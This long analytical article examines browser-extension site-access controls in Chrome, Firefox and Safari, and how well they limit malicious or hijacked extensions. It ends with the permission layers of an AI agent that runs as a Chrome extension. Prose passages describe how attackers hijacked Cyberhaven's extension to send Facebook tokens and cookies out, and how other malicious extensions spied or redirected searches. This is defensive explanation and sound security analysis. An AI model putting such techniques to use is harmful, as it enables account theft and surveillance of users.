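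This is a good argument for better store review but a weak one against the settings, which can also limit the damage when a trustworthy extension changes hands or an attacker takes over its developer's account. But Miagkov is probably right that most people won't adjust them. One developer in the thread said he simply installs extensions he trusts and removes any he stops trusting.

There is no sign that the new menu had reached all users by late 2026. In February 2025, Dunk wrote that the team was very early in its experiments and wasn't yet testing the menu in the stable version of Chrome. In July he didn't think the number of users with the menu had changed significantly. He had also said that Google should be able to confirm when the rollout was complete, but Google's running list of changes for extension developers contained no such notice in September 2026. The list's latest entry about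 the menu, from 2025, describes it as experimental. *What's new in web extensions* (Mihajlija, 2026), Google's summary of that year's conference news, doesn't mention the menu.

Google may be reconsidering the defaults. In October 2026, Pixel Magazine's *Chrome prepara mudança séria nas permissões das extensões* relayed an Android Police report about a test in Chrome Canary. In the test, when a user installs an extension, a prompt offers two choices, "when you click the extension" and "always on all sites", with the first already selected.

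This would have a much larger effect than a new menu, because it would also apply to people who never change a setting. Many more people would also encounter broken extensions. Pixel Magazine expects ad blockers, grammar checkers and password managers would seem faulty to anyone who accepted the default without reading it, particularly because the prompt appears only once. Google had not announced a date for the stable version. Later that month, Rijo (2026), in *Browser extension permissions*, still described access to all sites as something the user grants once, at installation.

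### Blocking one extension on one site

None of the three settings lets a user allow an extension everywhere except on one site. "On specific sites" is a list of permitted sites, so a person who wants a grammar checker to work everywhere except on their bank's site would have to list every other site they use.

Tassinari (2025), a web developer, describes this problem in *"extensions-menu-access-control" allow to disable one extension on one website*. The grammar checker Grammarly was altering pages he was building, so he wanted to turn it off there. He tried the new menu, but it could only block all extensions on the site, including one he needed for his work.

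Dunk answered that Google had no plans to add this. The team had considered it but decided that it would create too many possible states, when many users already have trouble understanding when extensions can run. That concern is reasonable for a menu that everyone sees, but people still have no simple way to keep one extension away from one sensitive site, which is a common wish. Tassinari gave his bank as an example, though he thought that blocking all extensions might be a good option there.

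### Administrators' rules

Companies and schools can do what Tassinari wanted. An administrator who manages Chrome for an organisation can use a policy called `ExtensionSettings`, which includes a list of blocked hosts and a list of allowed hosts. The administrator can apply these lists to one extension or to all of them. For example, this policy keeps extensions away from a company's own sites, except for its public help pages:

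```json
{
  "*": {
    "runtime_blocked_hosts": ["*://*.example.com"],
    "runtime_allowed_hosts": ["*://help.example.com"]
  }
}
```

The asterisk on the second line makes this the default for all extensions. To restrict only one, the administrator would replace the asterisk with that extension's identifier. On a blocked host, an extension can't insert scripts, read cookies or change network requests, even if its manifest requires access to the host and the user has chosen "on all sites".

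The allowed list only makes exceptions to the blocked list, so it doesn't give an extension access to sites it never requested. For example, the exception for `help.example.com` doesn't let an extension that requests only `news.example.org` access `help.example.com`.

This approach suits organisations because an administrator usually knows which sites hold sensitive data and can protect them without asking each employee to change a setting. They also don't need to predict every site that an extension might legitimately need. However, a sensitive site has no protection until someone adds it to the list.

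Tighter rules can also disrupt tools that organisations depend on. In November, Cubbins (2026) reported in *Google rolls back strict Chrome 155 extension restrictions following feedback* that Google had withdrawn a Chrome 155 restriction after it broke enterprise extensions that used the `debugger` API.

Chromium doesn't withhold sites from extensions that an administrator installs through an organisation's policy, so an employee can't switch such an extension to "on click". This is a more likely reason for greyed-out site access options than the one Chrome Story gives, which is that the extension's developer has required access to every site and Chrome has locked the setting. Chrome Story's explanation is probably wrong, because the settings exist to let users withhold sites that a developer requires.

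## Runtime requests and the defaults in Chrome, Firefox and Safari

An extension may lack access to a site because its developer made the site optional or because the user withheld it. In either case, the extension can ask for access while it is running. In Chrome, `permissions.request` opens a dialog, and `permissions.addHostAccessRequest` shows a message in the toolbar that the user can ignore.

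How often an extension has to ask for site access depends on what the browser grants at installation. Chrome grants access to every required site, Safari grants access to none, and Firefox switched from Safari's approach to Chrome's in 2024.

### Asking with a dialog

Suppose a translation extension requires access to `example.com` and lists `https://*/*` under `optional_host_permissions`. The second pattern gives it no access at first, but it lets the extension request any encrypted site later. Google recommends this pattern to developers who can't tell in advance which sites their extension will need. The code for a request might look like this:

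```js
translateButton.addEventListener("click", async () => {
  const allowed = await chrome.permissions.request({
    origins: ["https://news.example.org/*"]
  });
  if (allowed) translatePage();
});
```

Chrome accepts the request only in response to a user gesture, here a click on the extension's own button. If the new access carries a warning the user hasn't already accepted, Chrome shows a dialog. The extension then learns whether the user agreed. It can use the same function to request access to a required site if the user has withheld that access.

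One request can cover several sites and API permissions. In Firefox, the user must accept or refuse them all together, according to Extension Workshop's *Requesting the right permissions*, a guide on Mozilla's site for extension developers.

Once the user accepts, the extension has the same standing access as if the user had granted it at installation. But the user makes the decision later, and usually knows more about why the extension requests access.

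Apple's *Create web extensions for Safari* (2026), a conference talk, demonstrates runtime requests with an extension that keeps people off distracting websites. The extension can block a site without having access to it, but it needs access to redirect the user to its own page. Its developer can't know which sites people find distracting, so the extension makes access to every site optional and requests it when the user adds a site to the block list. The prompt makes sense to the user because they have just typed in the site's name.

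Asking later also lets an extension cope with a refusal. Extension Workshop gives the example of a note-taking extension that can attach a small map to a note. If the extension asks for the user's location when they first try to add a map, and they refuse, it can still save the note without the map.

Optional permissions make updates easier for developers, because adding one never causes Chrome to disable the extension. According to Google's documentation, the advantage of required permissions is that developers can rely on having them, but since Chrome 70 users have been able to withhold site access even when an extension requires it. Some permissions, including `debugger` and `proxy`, can't be optional in Chrome, so an extension that uses either of those two has to require it.

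### Giving up access and regaining it

An extension can give up an optional permission by calling `permissions.remove`. Google advises developers to do this when they no longer need the permission. But if the extension later requests the same permission, Chrome usually restores it without showing the dialog again.

This happens because `permissions.remove` takes the permission out of the active set but leaves it in Chromium's separate record of what the user has granted. When the extension requests the permission again, Chromium finds it in that record and doesn't prompt the user.

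Suppose the translation extension gives up access to a news site after translating an article. A month later, the user clicks "Translate" on the same site, and the extension gets its access back immediately. This is convenient, and a new dialog every time might discourage developers from giving up access at all. But if the developer had sold the extension in the meantime, the new owner could regain access when the user clicked something in the extension, and the user wouldn't see a prompt saying what the click allowed.

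Giving up access still offers some protection because, as with `activeTab`, an attacker who takes over the extension has to wait for a suitable click. Chrome asks again only if the user revokes the permission themselves, since the extension can't remove it from the record of what the user granted.

The same record spares users a second approval if an update turns an optional permission they have already granted into a required one.

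### Asking with a message in the toolbar

An extension can call `permissions.addHostAccessRequest` without a user gesture. In Google's sample code, the extension watches for a tab to open a shop's checkout page. If it lacks access to the shop, it adds a request, and Chrome shows an "Allow" message next to the puzzle-piece icon, which the user can click or ignore.

A developer has to attach the request to a particular tab or to the document loaded in it. They can also supply a match pattern so that the request appears only on certain pages. According to Chromium's definition of the function, Chrome shows the request only if the extension is eligible for access to the site. An extension can't use the function to ask for sites its manifest doesn't cover.

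The request disappears when the tab moves to another origin. If the user moves from the checkout page to another page in the shop, the extension has to withdraw the request by calling `permissions.removeHostAccessRequest`. If the user accepts the request, the extension gets persistent access to the top page's origin, even after the tab closes.

| | `permissions.request` | `permissions.addHostAccessRequest` |
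|---|---|---|
| What starts it | A user gesture | The extension's own code |
| Interruption | A dialog, unless the user has already accepted the same warnings | A message in the toolbar |
| Scope | One or more sites, and API permissions if the developer includes them | The origin of the page in one tab |
| Duration of access | Until someone removes it | Until someone removes it |

Without the gesture requirement, an extension could pester people with requests on every page. To prevent this, Chrome may limit how many requests an extension can make, and users can stop an extension from showing them. Google also warns developers that people are likely to ignore extensions that ask too often.

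The toolbar message is narrower than the dialog, which an extension could use to ask for access to every site at once. But neither offers temporary access. Someone who wants a coupon extension to check a single purchase might click "Allow" and give it standing access to the shop. If they clicked the extension's icon instead, it would get access only until the tab left the site.

Developers also can't rely on the toolbar message yet. Chrome has supported the function since version 133, but it does nothing for users who don't have the redesigned extensions menu. For them, an extension still has to use the dialog or wait for a click on its icon.

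### What each browser grants at installation

Chrome, Firefox and Safari all let users revoke an extension's access to the sites it requires, but their defaults differ. The table covers Manifest V3 extensions and draws on MDN's *host_permissions* for what the install prompts contain.

| Browser | Does the install prompt list required sites? | Does the extension get access to them at installation? |
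|---|---|---|
| Chrome | Yes | Yes |
| Firefox up to version 126 | No | No |
| Firefox from version 127 | Yes | Yes |
| Safari | No | No |

Google told both developers and the public that it would change Chrome's default. In December 2020, Google's *Making Chrome extensions more private and secure* (2020) promised that from 2021 users, not extensions, would decide which websites an extension could access. VentureBeat's *Google will change how Chrome extensions access data in 2021* (2020) reported that users could still allow an extension on every site, but that this would no longer be the default.

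Google didn't make that change, but in October 2026 it was testing an install prompt in Chrome Canary that would do much of what Google had promised in 2020.

### How Firefox reversed its default

When Mozilla adopted Manifest V3, it made every host permission optional in practice. Developers could list a site under `host_permissions`, but Firefox didn't grant access or mention the site when the user installed the extension. The user had to turn on access in Firefox's settings, or the extension had to request it.

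In *Automatic activeTab for ungranted host permissions in MV3*, a Mozilla engineer who uses the name zombie proposed that clicking an extension's toolbar button should give it temporary access to the current site if the extension had requested access but the user hadn't granted it. Firefox would treat the extension as if it had declared `activeTab`. Mozilla added this in Firefox 105. Safari already did something similar, as did Chrome when a user chose "on click".

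The automatic grant suited extensions that people invoke, but not those that have to work in the background. In *Offer controls for MV3 host permissions during install flow*, a report in Mozilla's bug tracker, a developer called me+bz said their extension was useless without access to its sites and couldn't wait for someone to click the toolbar button. They wanted Firefox to let developers make site access mandatory, or at least to tell users during installation that they needed to grant it.

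Danny Lin, another developer in the discussion, was working on an extension that blocks malicious sites. It had to download a list of those sites as soon as the user installed it. It needed access to the server to do this, but it couldn't call `permissions.request` because the user hadn't clicked anything in the extension yet. A Mozilla engineer suggested opening a tab after installation with an explanation and a button. Lin replied that users might miss the tab or forget to press the button, and then the blocker might not work.

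This is a serious objection, because withholding access from a security tool can leave its user less safe. It is weaker for this download because, as the engineer pointed out, the extension wouldn't need a host permission if the server allowed requests from it. Lin answered that developers often keep such lists on public code-hosting services, whose settings they don't control.

Firefox's interface also confused users, according to a developer called Particle in Mozilla's *[Blog post] Manifest V3 Updates*, a discussion on its forum. Particle complained that the only sign of missing access was a tiny blue dot on the extensions button, and that even users who noticed it couldn't tell whether clicking the extension would grant access once or permanently. Particle also disliked the suggestion of opening a tab to ask for permission, because it might interrupt people.

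The wording in Firefox's settings was also unhelpful. When a commenter in *Add optional_host_permissions in mv3* tested an extension that listed Wikipedia as a required site, Firefox showed the site under "optional permissions for added functionality".

The problems were worse on phones. In *Updated MV3 addon fails*, the developer of a cookie editor reported that when their extension requested access in Firefox for Android, there was no error, but no prompt appeared. Another developer in the discussion found no way to grant access in the extension's permissions tab.

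Developers could avoid many of these problems by continuing to use Manifest V2 in Firefox, where it still granted access to sites at installation. In the forum discussion *Request permissions at install time manifest v3*, someone who had written more than ten extensions recommended using Manifest V3 for Chrome and V2 for Firefox, as they did themselves, and the developer who had asked for help decided to do the same. They had no deadline to switch, since Mozilla's *Manifest V3 updates landed in Firefox 127* (2024) repeated that Mozilla had no plans to drop V2. Firefox's stricter default for Manifest V3 therefore gave developers a reason to avoid V3 in Firefox.

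Mozilla announced the reversal in May 2024. Its *Manifest V3 Updates* (2024) explained that users and developers had found the handling of host permissions a major hurdle. From Firefox 127, released that June, the install prompt listed the sites an extension required, and accepting it granted access to them. Users could still revoke access to a site, which Firefox had never allowed for Manifest V2 extensions, so Mozilla told developers to keep checking whether their extensions had access.

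Mozilla presented this change as temporary. In *Grant origin permissions during install for mv3*, zombie called it a "temporary stopgap" until Firefox had a better install flow, which would grant only some sites by default. A Mozilla developer had described such a flow to me+bz. Users could choose individual sites during installation, and Firefox would preselect them all if the extension asked for only a few, probably up to six or ten. Mozilla later lowered the priority of this work and left the report open.

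MDN notes that even under the new default, Firefox doesn't show users the additional sites that an update to a Manifest V3 extension requests. Developers therefore can't assume that users have approved the new sites, and users may not know that the extension has requested them.

Firefox 128 then added `optional_host_permissions`, which Safari and Chrome already supported. This let developers separate the sites an extension needs immediately from those it might request later, and let Firefox treat the two groups differently.

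### Safari's prompts

Safari still withholds access to required sites. When the user visits a site that an extension has requested, Safari puts a badge on the extension's toolbar button. Clicking the button opens an alert where the user can allow access. If the user does, Safari tints the icon to show that the extension is active on the page.

The user also chooses how long access lasts. Apple's *Managing Safari web extension permissions* lists four choices on a Mac: allow access for a single use, allow it for the rest of the day, allow it on all websites, or deny it. On an iPhone, the user finds the permission options by opening the More menu and selecting the extension.

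iDownloadBlog's *How to allow or block a Safari extension on a specific website* gives a slightly different set: one day on the current site, always on that site, or always on every site. The two lists may describe different versions of Safari or different kinds of extension. Both include a one-day choice, which Chrome doesn't offer. Whatever the user first chooses, they can later set each site to "Ask", "Allow" or "Deny" in Safari's settings. This makes it possible to block one extension on one site, which Chrome's ordinary settings don't allow.

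A grant in Safari can also apply more widely than the user expects. Since Safari 17, allowing an extension on a site has applied to all the user's profiles and to private browsing. Someone who keeps separate work and home profiles can't use the prompt to allow an extension on a site in only one of them.

Developers can avoid most of these prompts by using `activeTab`. In the *Safari and Web Technologies Group Lab* (2026), a panel of Apple engineers recommended it to developers who request access to too many sites because they can't predict where people will use their extension.

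### The arguments for and against withholding access

Apple withholds access by default, arguing that users should decide which sites an extension can reach because browsing can expose personal data. The default matters most for people who never open their browser's settings. An extension they install in Safari and forget about can't access their bank or email unless they allow it.

A prompt on a particular site also gives the user a more specific question to answer than an install prompt does. They can see the page the extension would read, and they may know whether they want its help there. A one-day grant also expires even if the user forgets about it.

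But prompts are a burden for extensions that need to work everywhere. In *Safari setting "Always allow on this/every website*, a user called mikebore complained of repeatedly finding the password manager 1Password inactive on a page and having to click its icon and choose a setting each time. Allowing every website would have solved the problem, but Safari showed a strong warning about that choice. The user wondered whether to keep allowing sites one at a time until most of the common ones were covered.

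1Password's staff answered that the extension needed access to all pages to fill in passwords properly. In mikebore's thread, one of them also pointed out that other browsers make people either give an extension access to all sites or not install it.

Some developers tell users to grant access to every site. Clay, an app that shows information about people in the user's network, tells users of its Safari extension to select "Always Allow on Every Website", partly because this prevents repeated prompts. The advice may be sensible for that product, but users who follow it can end up granting as much access as Chrome would have granted automatically.

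Ajay (2025) reported in *Browser asking for permissions for every site* that a test version of Safari prompted users about every site when an extension listed all sites as optional. If a browser does this, users see requests for access that the extension may never need, and developers lose much of the benefit of asking only when a feature requires it.

Firefox's reversal is not strong evidence against withholding access, because its interface made the policy harder to use. The install prompt didn't mention the sites, it was unclear what a click meant, and the Android version sometimes offered no way to grant access at all. Mozilla's unfinished plan would have fixed the first problem by letting people choose sites during installation. It might not have helped an extension that needs every site, since Firefox would apparently have preselected sites only for extensions that requested a few.

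The case for withholding access by default is strongest where few extensions need it and a mistake could expose a lot. Mozilla has since applied a strict default to files on the user's computer. Before Firefox 153, an extension with access to all websites could also read local files that the user opened in the browser. Mozilla's *Firefox 153 WebExtensions API updates* (2026) describes a separate permission for this, which is off by default even for extensions already installed. Mozilla warned developers that extensions relying on local files would be unable to use them until users turned the permission on.

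## How far limited access protects users

Restricting an extension's access to sites protects users most when an attacker takes control of an extension that was originally legitimate. It also limits how much data a legitimate extension can collect. It protects users least against extensions that are malicious from the start, because their developers can design them so that users click them on the pages the developers want to read.

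| Extension | Standing access | Chosen sites | `activeTab` or "on click" |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious from the start | It can read every site it requested, starting at installation. | It can read the sites on the user's list, which probably include the one it claims to help with. | It can read a site once the user clicks it there. |
| Honest, then taken over | The attacker gets all the access the old version had, without a prompt. | The attacker gets only the listed sites. | The attacker has to wait for a click on a site worth attacking. |
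| Honest, but collects too much | The developer can record what the user does on every requested site. | The record covers only the listed sites. | The record covers only sites where the user clicked, until the tab leaves them. |

### Extensions that are malicious from the start

A malicious developer has no reason to choose `activeTab` and can require access to every site instead. Only the user's settings or the browser's defaults can limit that developer's extension.

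In *What is in the Chrome Web Store?*, Hsu, Tran and Fass (2024) used historical data to study extensions that were malicious, broke the store's policies or had security flaws. They found that such extensions stay in the store for years and affect almost 350 million users. TechSpot reports their figure for malware alone as 280 million people over three years, and contrasts it with Google's statement that less than 1% of installations in 2024 included malware. Both could be true, since even 1% of a very large number of installations can affect many people.

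Seetharam and colleagues searched for malicious extensions among 5,551 that had AI-related words in their name or description and came out between January and mid-September 2025. They examined the developers' history, the code and the network traffic, and then reviewed the suspicious ones by hand. They found 154 malicious extensions that nobody had reported before. Adding 187 from earlier reports brought the total to 341, of which 29 presented themselves as generative AI tools.

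One of these, Supersonic AI, offered to write replies and summaries in Gmail and Outlook. When the user clicked "Generate reply", it sent the whole email thread to an outside server. It also sent emails that the user had only opened. In the researchers' test, one of those emails contained a LinkedIn verification code, which an attacker could have used to take over the account.

Most AI writing tools have to send emails to a server, and Supersonic AI advertised summaries, so sending them doesn't prove bad intent. The researchers also suspected that its reviews were fake. Only 26 people had installed it.

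With the "on click" setting, Supersonic AI couldn't have read any email until the user clicked its icon, but people who install an email assistant will click it in their email. The grant then lasts until the tab leaves the site, so someone who keeps Gmail open all day would still have exposed the LinkedIn code. Adding Gmail to a list of chosen sites would have exposed it too. Either setting would still keep an extension like this off the user's banking site.

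Some attacks don't need access to any site, so Chrome's site settings wouldn't prevent them. The extension Perplexity Search changed the browser's search settings so that everything the user typed into the address bar went to the attacker's server first. The server then forwarded the user to the real Perplexity, an AI search service, so nothing seemed wrong. Another extension, Photoroom AI Photo Editor, opened a tab as soon as the user installed it. The tab showed a false error message and a button to download a different browser, for which the attacker earned a commission. Seetharam and colleagues linked the extension to at least 68 similar ones.

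A malicious extension can also ask for access. When Tyler and De Oliveira Nunes tested their cookie-stealing extensions in Firefox, the Manifest V3 version had to request access to sites after installation, because Firefox still withheld it by default. They thought an attacker would probably get around this by imitating a legitimate service. They didn't test this on users, but it is plausible, because a fake cookie manager has an obvious reason to request access to cookies.

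Withholding access probably does more against extensions that spy in the background. Of the 517 malicious extensions in Pantelaios and Kapravelos's conversion study, 356 collected data about users, 112 replaced advertisements, and only a handful stole login details. Some did more than one of these things.

Manifest V3 didn't eliminate any of these types. Among the converted extensions that still worked, 123 collected user data and 77 replaced advertisements. But the researchers ran each extension on sites that its manifest allowed, so they measured the effect of V3's technical changes, not the effect of withholding access to sites. An extension that replaces advertisements on every page would fail on most pages if the user had to click the extension first.

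The study may also have missed some malicious behaviour. The researchers found extensions that waited three days before downloading their malicious code, and others that stopped working when they detected a university's network.

### The takeover of Cyberhaven's extension

Cyberhaven sells software that prevents employees from misusing company data. Its Chrome extension can detect, for example, when someone tries to copy files from an important database into an insecure tool, according to SiliconANGLE's *Hackers compromise Chrome extensions with 400,000+ users* (2024). On 24 December 2024, attackers gained the ability to publish new versions of the extension.

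According to Cyberhaven's preliminary analysis (2024), the attackers sent a phishing email to the extension's public support address. An employee followed the link to a genuine Google page and unintentionally authorised an application called "Privacy Policy Extension", which gave the attackers access to the company's Chrome Web Store account. The employee had multi-factor authentication turned on, but Google never asked for the second factor. The attackers then copied the real extension, added their own code and uploaded it as a new version, which passed the store's review.

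The company's two accounts of that day differ slightly. Ting (2024), the chief executive, wrote in *Cyberhaven's Chrome extension security incident and what we're doing about it* that the attack had compromised the employee's credentials for the store. According to the preliminary analysis, the attackers never obtained his Google credentials, which they didn't need once he had authorised their application.

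The malicious code was active from 1:32 a.m. UTC on 25 December until 2:50 a.m. on 26 December, a little over 25 hours. Cyberhaven's security team discovered it shortly before midnight on the 25th and removed the malicious version within an hour. Only Chrome-based browsers that updated the extension automatically during those 25 hours received the code.

SiliconANGLE's figure of more than 400,000 users covers everyone who had the compromised extensions. Cyberhaven didn't publish how many people received the malicious version and wrote only that it reached a portion of its customers.

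Once installed, the code contacted the attackers' server and downloaded instructions that named a target website. On the machines Cyberhaven examined, this was always Facebook. When a logged-in user visited Facebook, the extension:

- copied the user's access token, a value that lets a program act for the account
- used Facebook's own functions to look up the user's account, business accounts and advertising accounts
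- sent all this to the attackers, along with the Facebook cookies

The code also watched for clicks on Facebook pages. After each click, it searched the page for a QR code and sent its address to the attackers, probably to help them get past two-factor authentication. Ting wrote that the attackers were after logins to social media advertising and AI platforms. The preliminary analysis found one request to ChatGPT, but the code did nothing with the reply.

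The campaign that hit Cyberhaven had other victims too. DomainTools' *Cyberhaven Breach Likely Part of a Long-Term Criminal Campaign* (2025) concluded that it had gone on for months and mostly targeted technology companies. In January, Cyberhaven's *Final analysis* (2025) cited a report by the consulting firm Booz Allen Hamilton that identified over 30 other extensions the attackers might have compromised. Together, these extensions had more than 2.6 million users.

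### Which limits would have stopped the theft

Requiring a click would have stopped most of the attack. The malicious code ran whenever a logged-in user opened Facebook. With a click required, it would have run only if the user clicked the extension's icon while on Facebook during those 25 hours, and few people would have had a reason to.

The click requirement protects users about equally well whether it comes from `activeTab` or from the user's "on click" setting. The user's setting would have survived the update. The attackers controlled the new version's manifest, so they could have replaced `activeTab` with access to every site, but Chrome would then have disabled the extension until each user approved the new warning.

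A list of chosen sites would have helped only if it left out Facebook. Even then, the attackers could have changed the target, because the code downloaded the target's name from their server. If a company had limited the extension to its own internal systems, those would have been the only targets left, and they might have been worth more than a Facebook account.

These limits on access don't suit Cyberhaven's product very well. An extension that detects leaks has to run wherever employees might send company data, including Facebook, and employees won't click it before leaking a file. If a company installed the extension through an administrator's policy, employees couldn't have switched it to "on click" anyway. An administrator could have blocked it on Facebook, but then it would have missed any files that employees uploaded there.

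Limited access would have suited some other compromised extensions better. Seetharam and colleagues' list of malicious AI-themed extensions includes ten from the security firm Secure Annex's investigation of the Cyberhaven attack. Judging by their names, most were chat assistants, and one summarised text with OpenAI's models. A tool that summarises a page can usually work with access granted only when the user clicks.

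The short duration also made a click requirement more useful, because over several months people would probably click most of their extensions on at least one sensitive site. Manus AI | Free AI Assistant, another extension in Seetharam and colleagues' study, stayed in the store for about three months. A related extension, which imitated the AI company DeepSeek, had two harmless versions before an update made it malicious. Its developer apparently planned this from the start, but limiting the extension's access would have protected users as much as in a takeover.

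Cyberhaven applied the same principle to its own staff after the attack. Several senior developers had permanent access to its Chrome Web Store account for publishing and troubleshooting. The company removed that access and set up an emergency account that its security team controls.

### Honest extensions that collect too much

Many developers request more access than their extensions need. In *Are chrome extensions compliant with the spirit of least privilege?*, Picazo-Sanchez, Ortiz-Martin and colleagues (2022) found that 39.8% of the Chrome Web Store extensions they tested followed the principle that a program should have only the access it needs. Seetharam and colleagues cite a 2025 analysis of more than 300,000 extensions, in which 51% requested overly broad access.

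*A Security Analysis of Browser Extensions* (2014) compared the permissions that Chrome extensions requested with the ones their code used. Almost half requested more than they used. Most of those had only one or two extra, which the researchers attributed to carelessness, but 192 had at least four. The researchers looked only at background scripts, so they may have counted some permissions as unused when an extension needed them in its popup.

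There don't appear to be any public counts of how many extensions use `activeTab`, or of how many request access to every site when `activeTab` would be enough. The second count would be more useful because it would show how much standing access developers could give up without losing features.

Developers may have little reason to give up broad access. *I have no idea how to make it safer* reports interviews with 21 extension developers. Many recognised that their extensions posed risks but lacked the knowledge or resources to reduce them, and had few incentives to try.

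Unneeded access does no harm until someone uses it. *Spying Chrome Extensions*, a pseudonymous researcher's report that hasn't been peer reviewed, identifies 287 extensions with 37 million users that leaked the addresses of pages people visited. An address can contain a name, a search term or a link that gives access to a private document. Many of the extensions misled users about the data they collected or denied collecting any, so they can't all be counted as honest.

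With `activeTab`, an honest developer who collects too much data gets a few scattered pages instead of a full browsing history. Temporary access probably protects users most reliably in this case, because the developer won't try to trick them into clicking.

But the site settings don't block every way to collect addresses. According to Chromium's security FAQ, an extension with the right API permissions can read the addresses of open tabs and entries in the browsing history. Such an extension could keep recording which pages the user visits even when set to "on click", though it couldn't read the pages themselves.

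### Whether people understand and use the limits

No public data seems to show how many people choose "on click" or "on specific sites". Research on what extension users know and how they protect themselves gives some indirect evidence.

Kariryaa, Savino and colleagues (2021), in *Understanding Users' Knowledge about the Privacy and Security of Browser Extensions*, surveyed 353 extension users through Prolific, a website for paid studies. 59% said they had taken no steps to keep their data safe from their extensions, and less than a third said they had. Those steps could include measures other than restricting site access, so probably far fewer had restricted it.

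Only about one in ten of the participants correctly answered that an ad blocker could read the passwords they used on websites. Forty percent said it couldn't, and the rest didn't know. The participants were 28 years old on average, and many had a background in computer science, so other people may know even less.

More than half did believe that a browser extension could read passwords and store them on a server. The researchers' explanation is that people judge an extension by its purpose, so they know that a password manager reads passwords but don't realise that an ad blocker has similar permissions. Someone who thinks this way has little reason to restrict an ad blocker or any other extension whose purpose sounds harmless.

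The researchers also tested whether install prompts help people understand what an extension can do. Participants judged whether an extension could do things such as block a page or change product links, first without a prompt and then after seeing the one from Chrome, Firefox or Safari. On five actions that the permissions allowed, they gained a point for each correct answer and lost one for each wrong one.

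The median score rose from two to three, but only because of people who saw Chrome's or Firefox's prompt. Those who saw Safari's did no better than before, even though it was the only prompt that mentioned passwords and credit cards, so more explicit wording evidently isn't enough by itself. Only 35% of participants remembered having seen a prompt like Chrome's before the survey.

There is some evidence that people restrict access when they can see how apps use it. Kariryaa and colleagues cite a study in which people reconsidered and restricted some permissions after a permission manager on their phones showed them which data their apps were accessing. This supports Google's plan to make site access more visible in Chrome's menu, although turning off an app's access to location, for example, is simpler than choosing websites for an extension.

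Research on encrypted DNS, a browser setting that hides the names of the sites a browser looks up, is less encouraging. In the studies covered by *A Systematic Survey of Empirical User Studies of Unintentional Information Disclosure* (2025), users mostly trusted the default and didn't change it because they worried something might break. Extension users have even more reason to worry about this, so the default at installation probably matters more than how easy the settings are to find.

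### Extensions that need standing access

Many of the most useful extensions need access to pages without waiting for a click. In Kariryaa and colleagues' survey, 85% of participants used an ad blocker and 26% used a password manager. Chromium's developers write in their FAQ that there is very little data they could block every extension from accessing, and give password managers as their example.

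Some extensions that run automatically can still work when limited to sites the user chooses. A shopping assistant can run on the few shops a person uses, and a grammar checker can run on their webmail and the site where they write documents. A password manager could also run only on sites where the user has an account, but this limit would protect the user less, because those are the sites an attacker would want most.

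A password manager could work with `activeTab` if people were willing to click its icon or press a shortcut at each login. It could still compare the site's address with the saved one to avoid filling in a password on a fake site. But it couldn't offer a password automatically, and it would fail when the login form is in a frame from another origin. People might then go back to choosing simple passwords they can remember, which could put them at greater risk than the extension would.

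Narrower interfaces would let the browser do the sensitive part of the work. With `declarativeNetRequest`, Manifest V3's rule-based interface for network requests, Chrome blocks advertisements without showing the requests to the ad blocker. A test extension that Tyler and De Oliveira Nunes built using only this interface could change cookies in web traffic but couldn't steal them.

So far, developers have mostly added this interface to the access they already had. Of the 2,114 extensions that used it in March 2024, 67.9% also had access to every site, and at least 14.5% could still read web requests through the older interface. Some of these extensions were probably still moving to Manifest V3. Others needed access to the page, for example to hide the empty space that a blocked advertisement leaves.

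The new interface also makes ad blockers less capable. Pantelaios and Kapravelos report that developers complain about limits on the number and type of rules, and about having to update the whole extension when their blocklists change. An ad blocker without standing access is safer if an attacker takes it over, but it may block fewer advertisements and trackers.

Browsers keep one extension from reading another's stored data, but when a password manager copies a password into a web page, any other extension with access to that site can read it. *Passwords and FIDO2 Are Meant To Be Secret* proposes a new browser interface that would protect passwords from malicious extensions. The password manager itself would still have all the passwords, so an attacker who took it over could steal them.

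Browsers could also withhold particular data instead of whole sites. Tyler and De Oliveira Nunes modified Chromium so that websites can mark a cookie as `BrowserOnly`, which hides it from all extensions, even those with access to every site. Because some extensions need to read cookies, the modified browser also supports a `Monitored` label, which lets a website detect when someone uses the cookie in a different browser.

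These labels would have prevented only part of the Cyberhaven theft. The attackers couldn't have used Facebook's session cookies in their own browsers, but the malicious code could still have read the page and requested account details while the user was logged in. The labels also work only if browsers support them and websites apply them to their cookies.

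## AI agents that run as browser extensions

An AI agent that runs as a browser extension has two layers of permissions. The browser controls which sites and functions the extension can use, as it does for any extension. The extension's own software limits what the agent may do with that access, for example by asking the user before the agent clicks anything on a new site. If that software fails or an attacker takes it over, only the browser's layer still protects the user.

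Claude in Chrome, from the AI company Anthropic, is a well-documented example. The user types a request in a side panel, and the Claude model reads pages, clicks, types and moves between sites to carry it out. It works in the user's ordinary browser, so it is logged in to the same sites as the user.

Suppose a user asks Claude to find a delivery date in their webmail and add it to their calendar. A pseudonymous developer, sshh12 (2026), in *Claude for Chrome Extension Internals (v1.0.56)*, read the extension's code and described the loop that follows:

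1. The extension sends Claude the request, with the addresses and titles of the tabs it is using.
2. Claude replies with an action, such as reading the page or clicking at a certain point.
3. The extension checks whether the user has allowed that action on that site, and asks if necessary.
4. If the user has allowed it, the extension performs the action and sends Claude the result.

The loop repeats until Claude replies without an action. Chrome is not involved in the third step because the extension already has the browser permissions it needs.

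### What Chrome grants the extension

Anthropic's *Get started with Claude in Chrome* lists 15 permissions that users have to grant, with a reason for each. These are the ones that matter most for what the agent can do:

| Permission | Anthropic's reason for it |
|---|---|
| `debugger` | Clicking, typing and taking screenshots |
| `scripting` | Reading the text of web pages |
| `tabs` and `tabGroups` | Opening, closing and switching tabs, and keeping Claude's tabs in a separate group |
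| `webNavigation` | Stepping in when Claude is on a high-risk website |
| `downloads` | Saving files and opening them |
| `nativeMessaging` | Working with Anthropic's programs on the same computer |
| `alarms` | Starting tasks at times the user has scheduled |

Most of the other seven do minor jobs, such as saving settings and playing notification sounds.

Anthropic's list doesn't include any match patterns, but the extension must have some access to sites because `scripting` gives none by itself. *Claude in Chrome*, an analysis by the security firm Zenity Labs, says the extension also requires `activeTab`, which Anthropic doesn't list. `activeTab` would add little to what the agent can reach, because the `debugger` permission is much broader.

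Chrome grants these permissions on a standing basis, so the extension keeps them between tasks. According to sshh12, the extension disconnects the debugger from all tabs when a task ends. Anthropic chose this behavior in its code, and Chrome would let the extension reconnect the debugger at any time.

### The debugger permission

The `debugger` permission lets an extension use the Chrome DevTools Protocol, a set of commands for inspecting and controlling web pages. Programmers normally use these commands to debug their own sites. An agent can use them to move the mouse, enter text and capture what is on the page.

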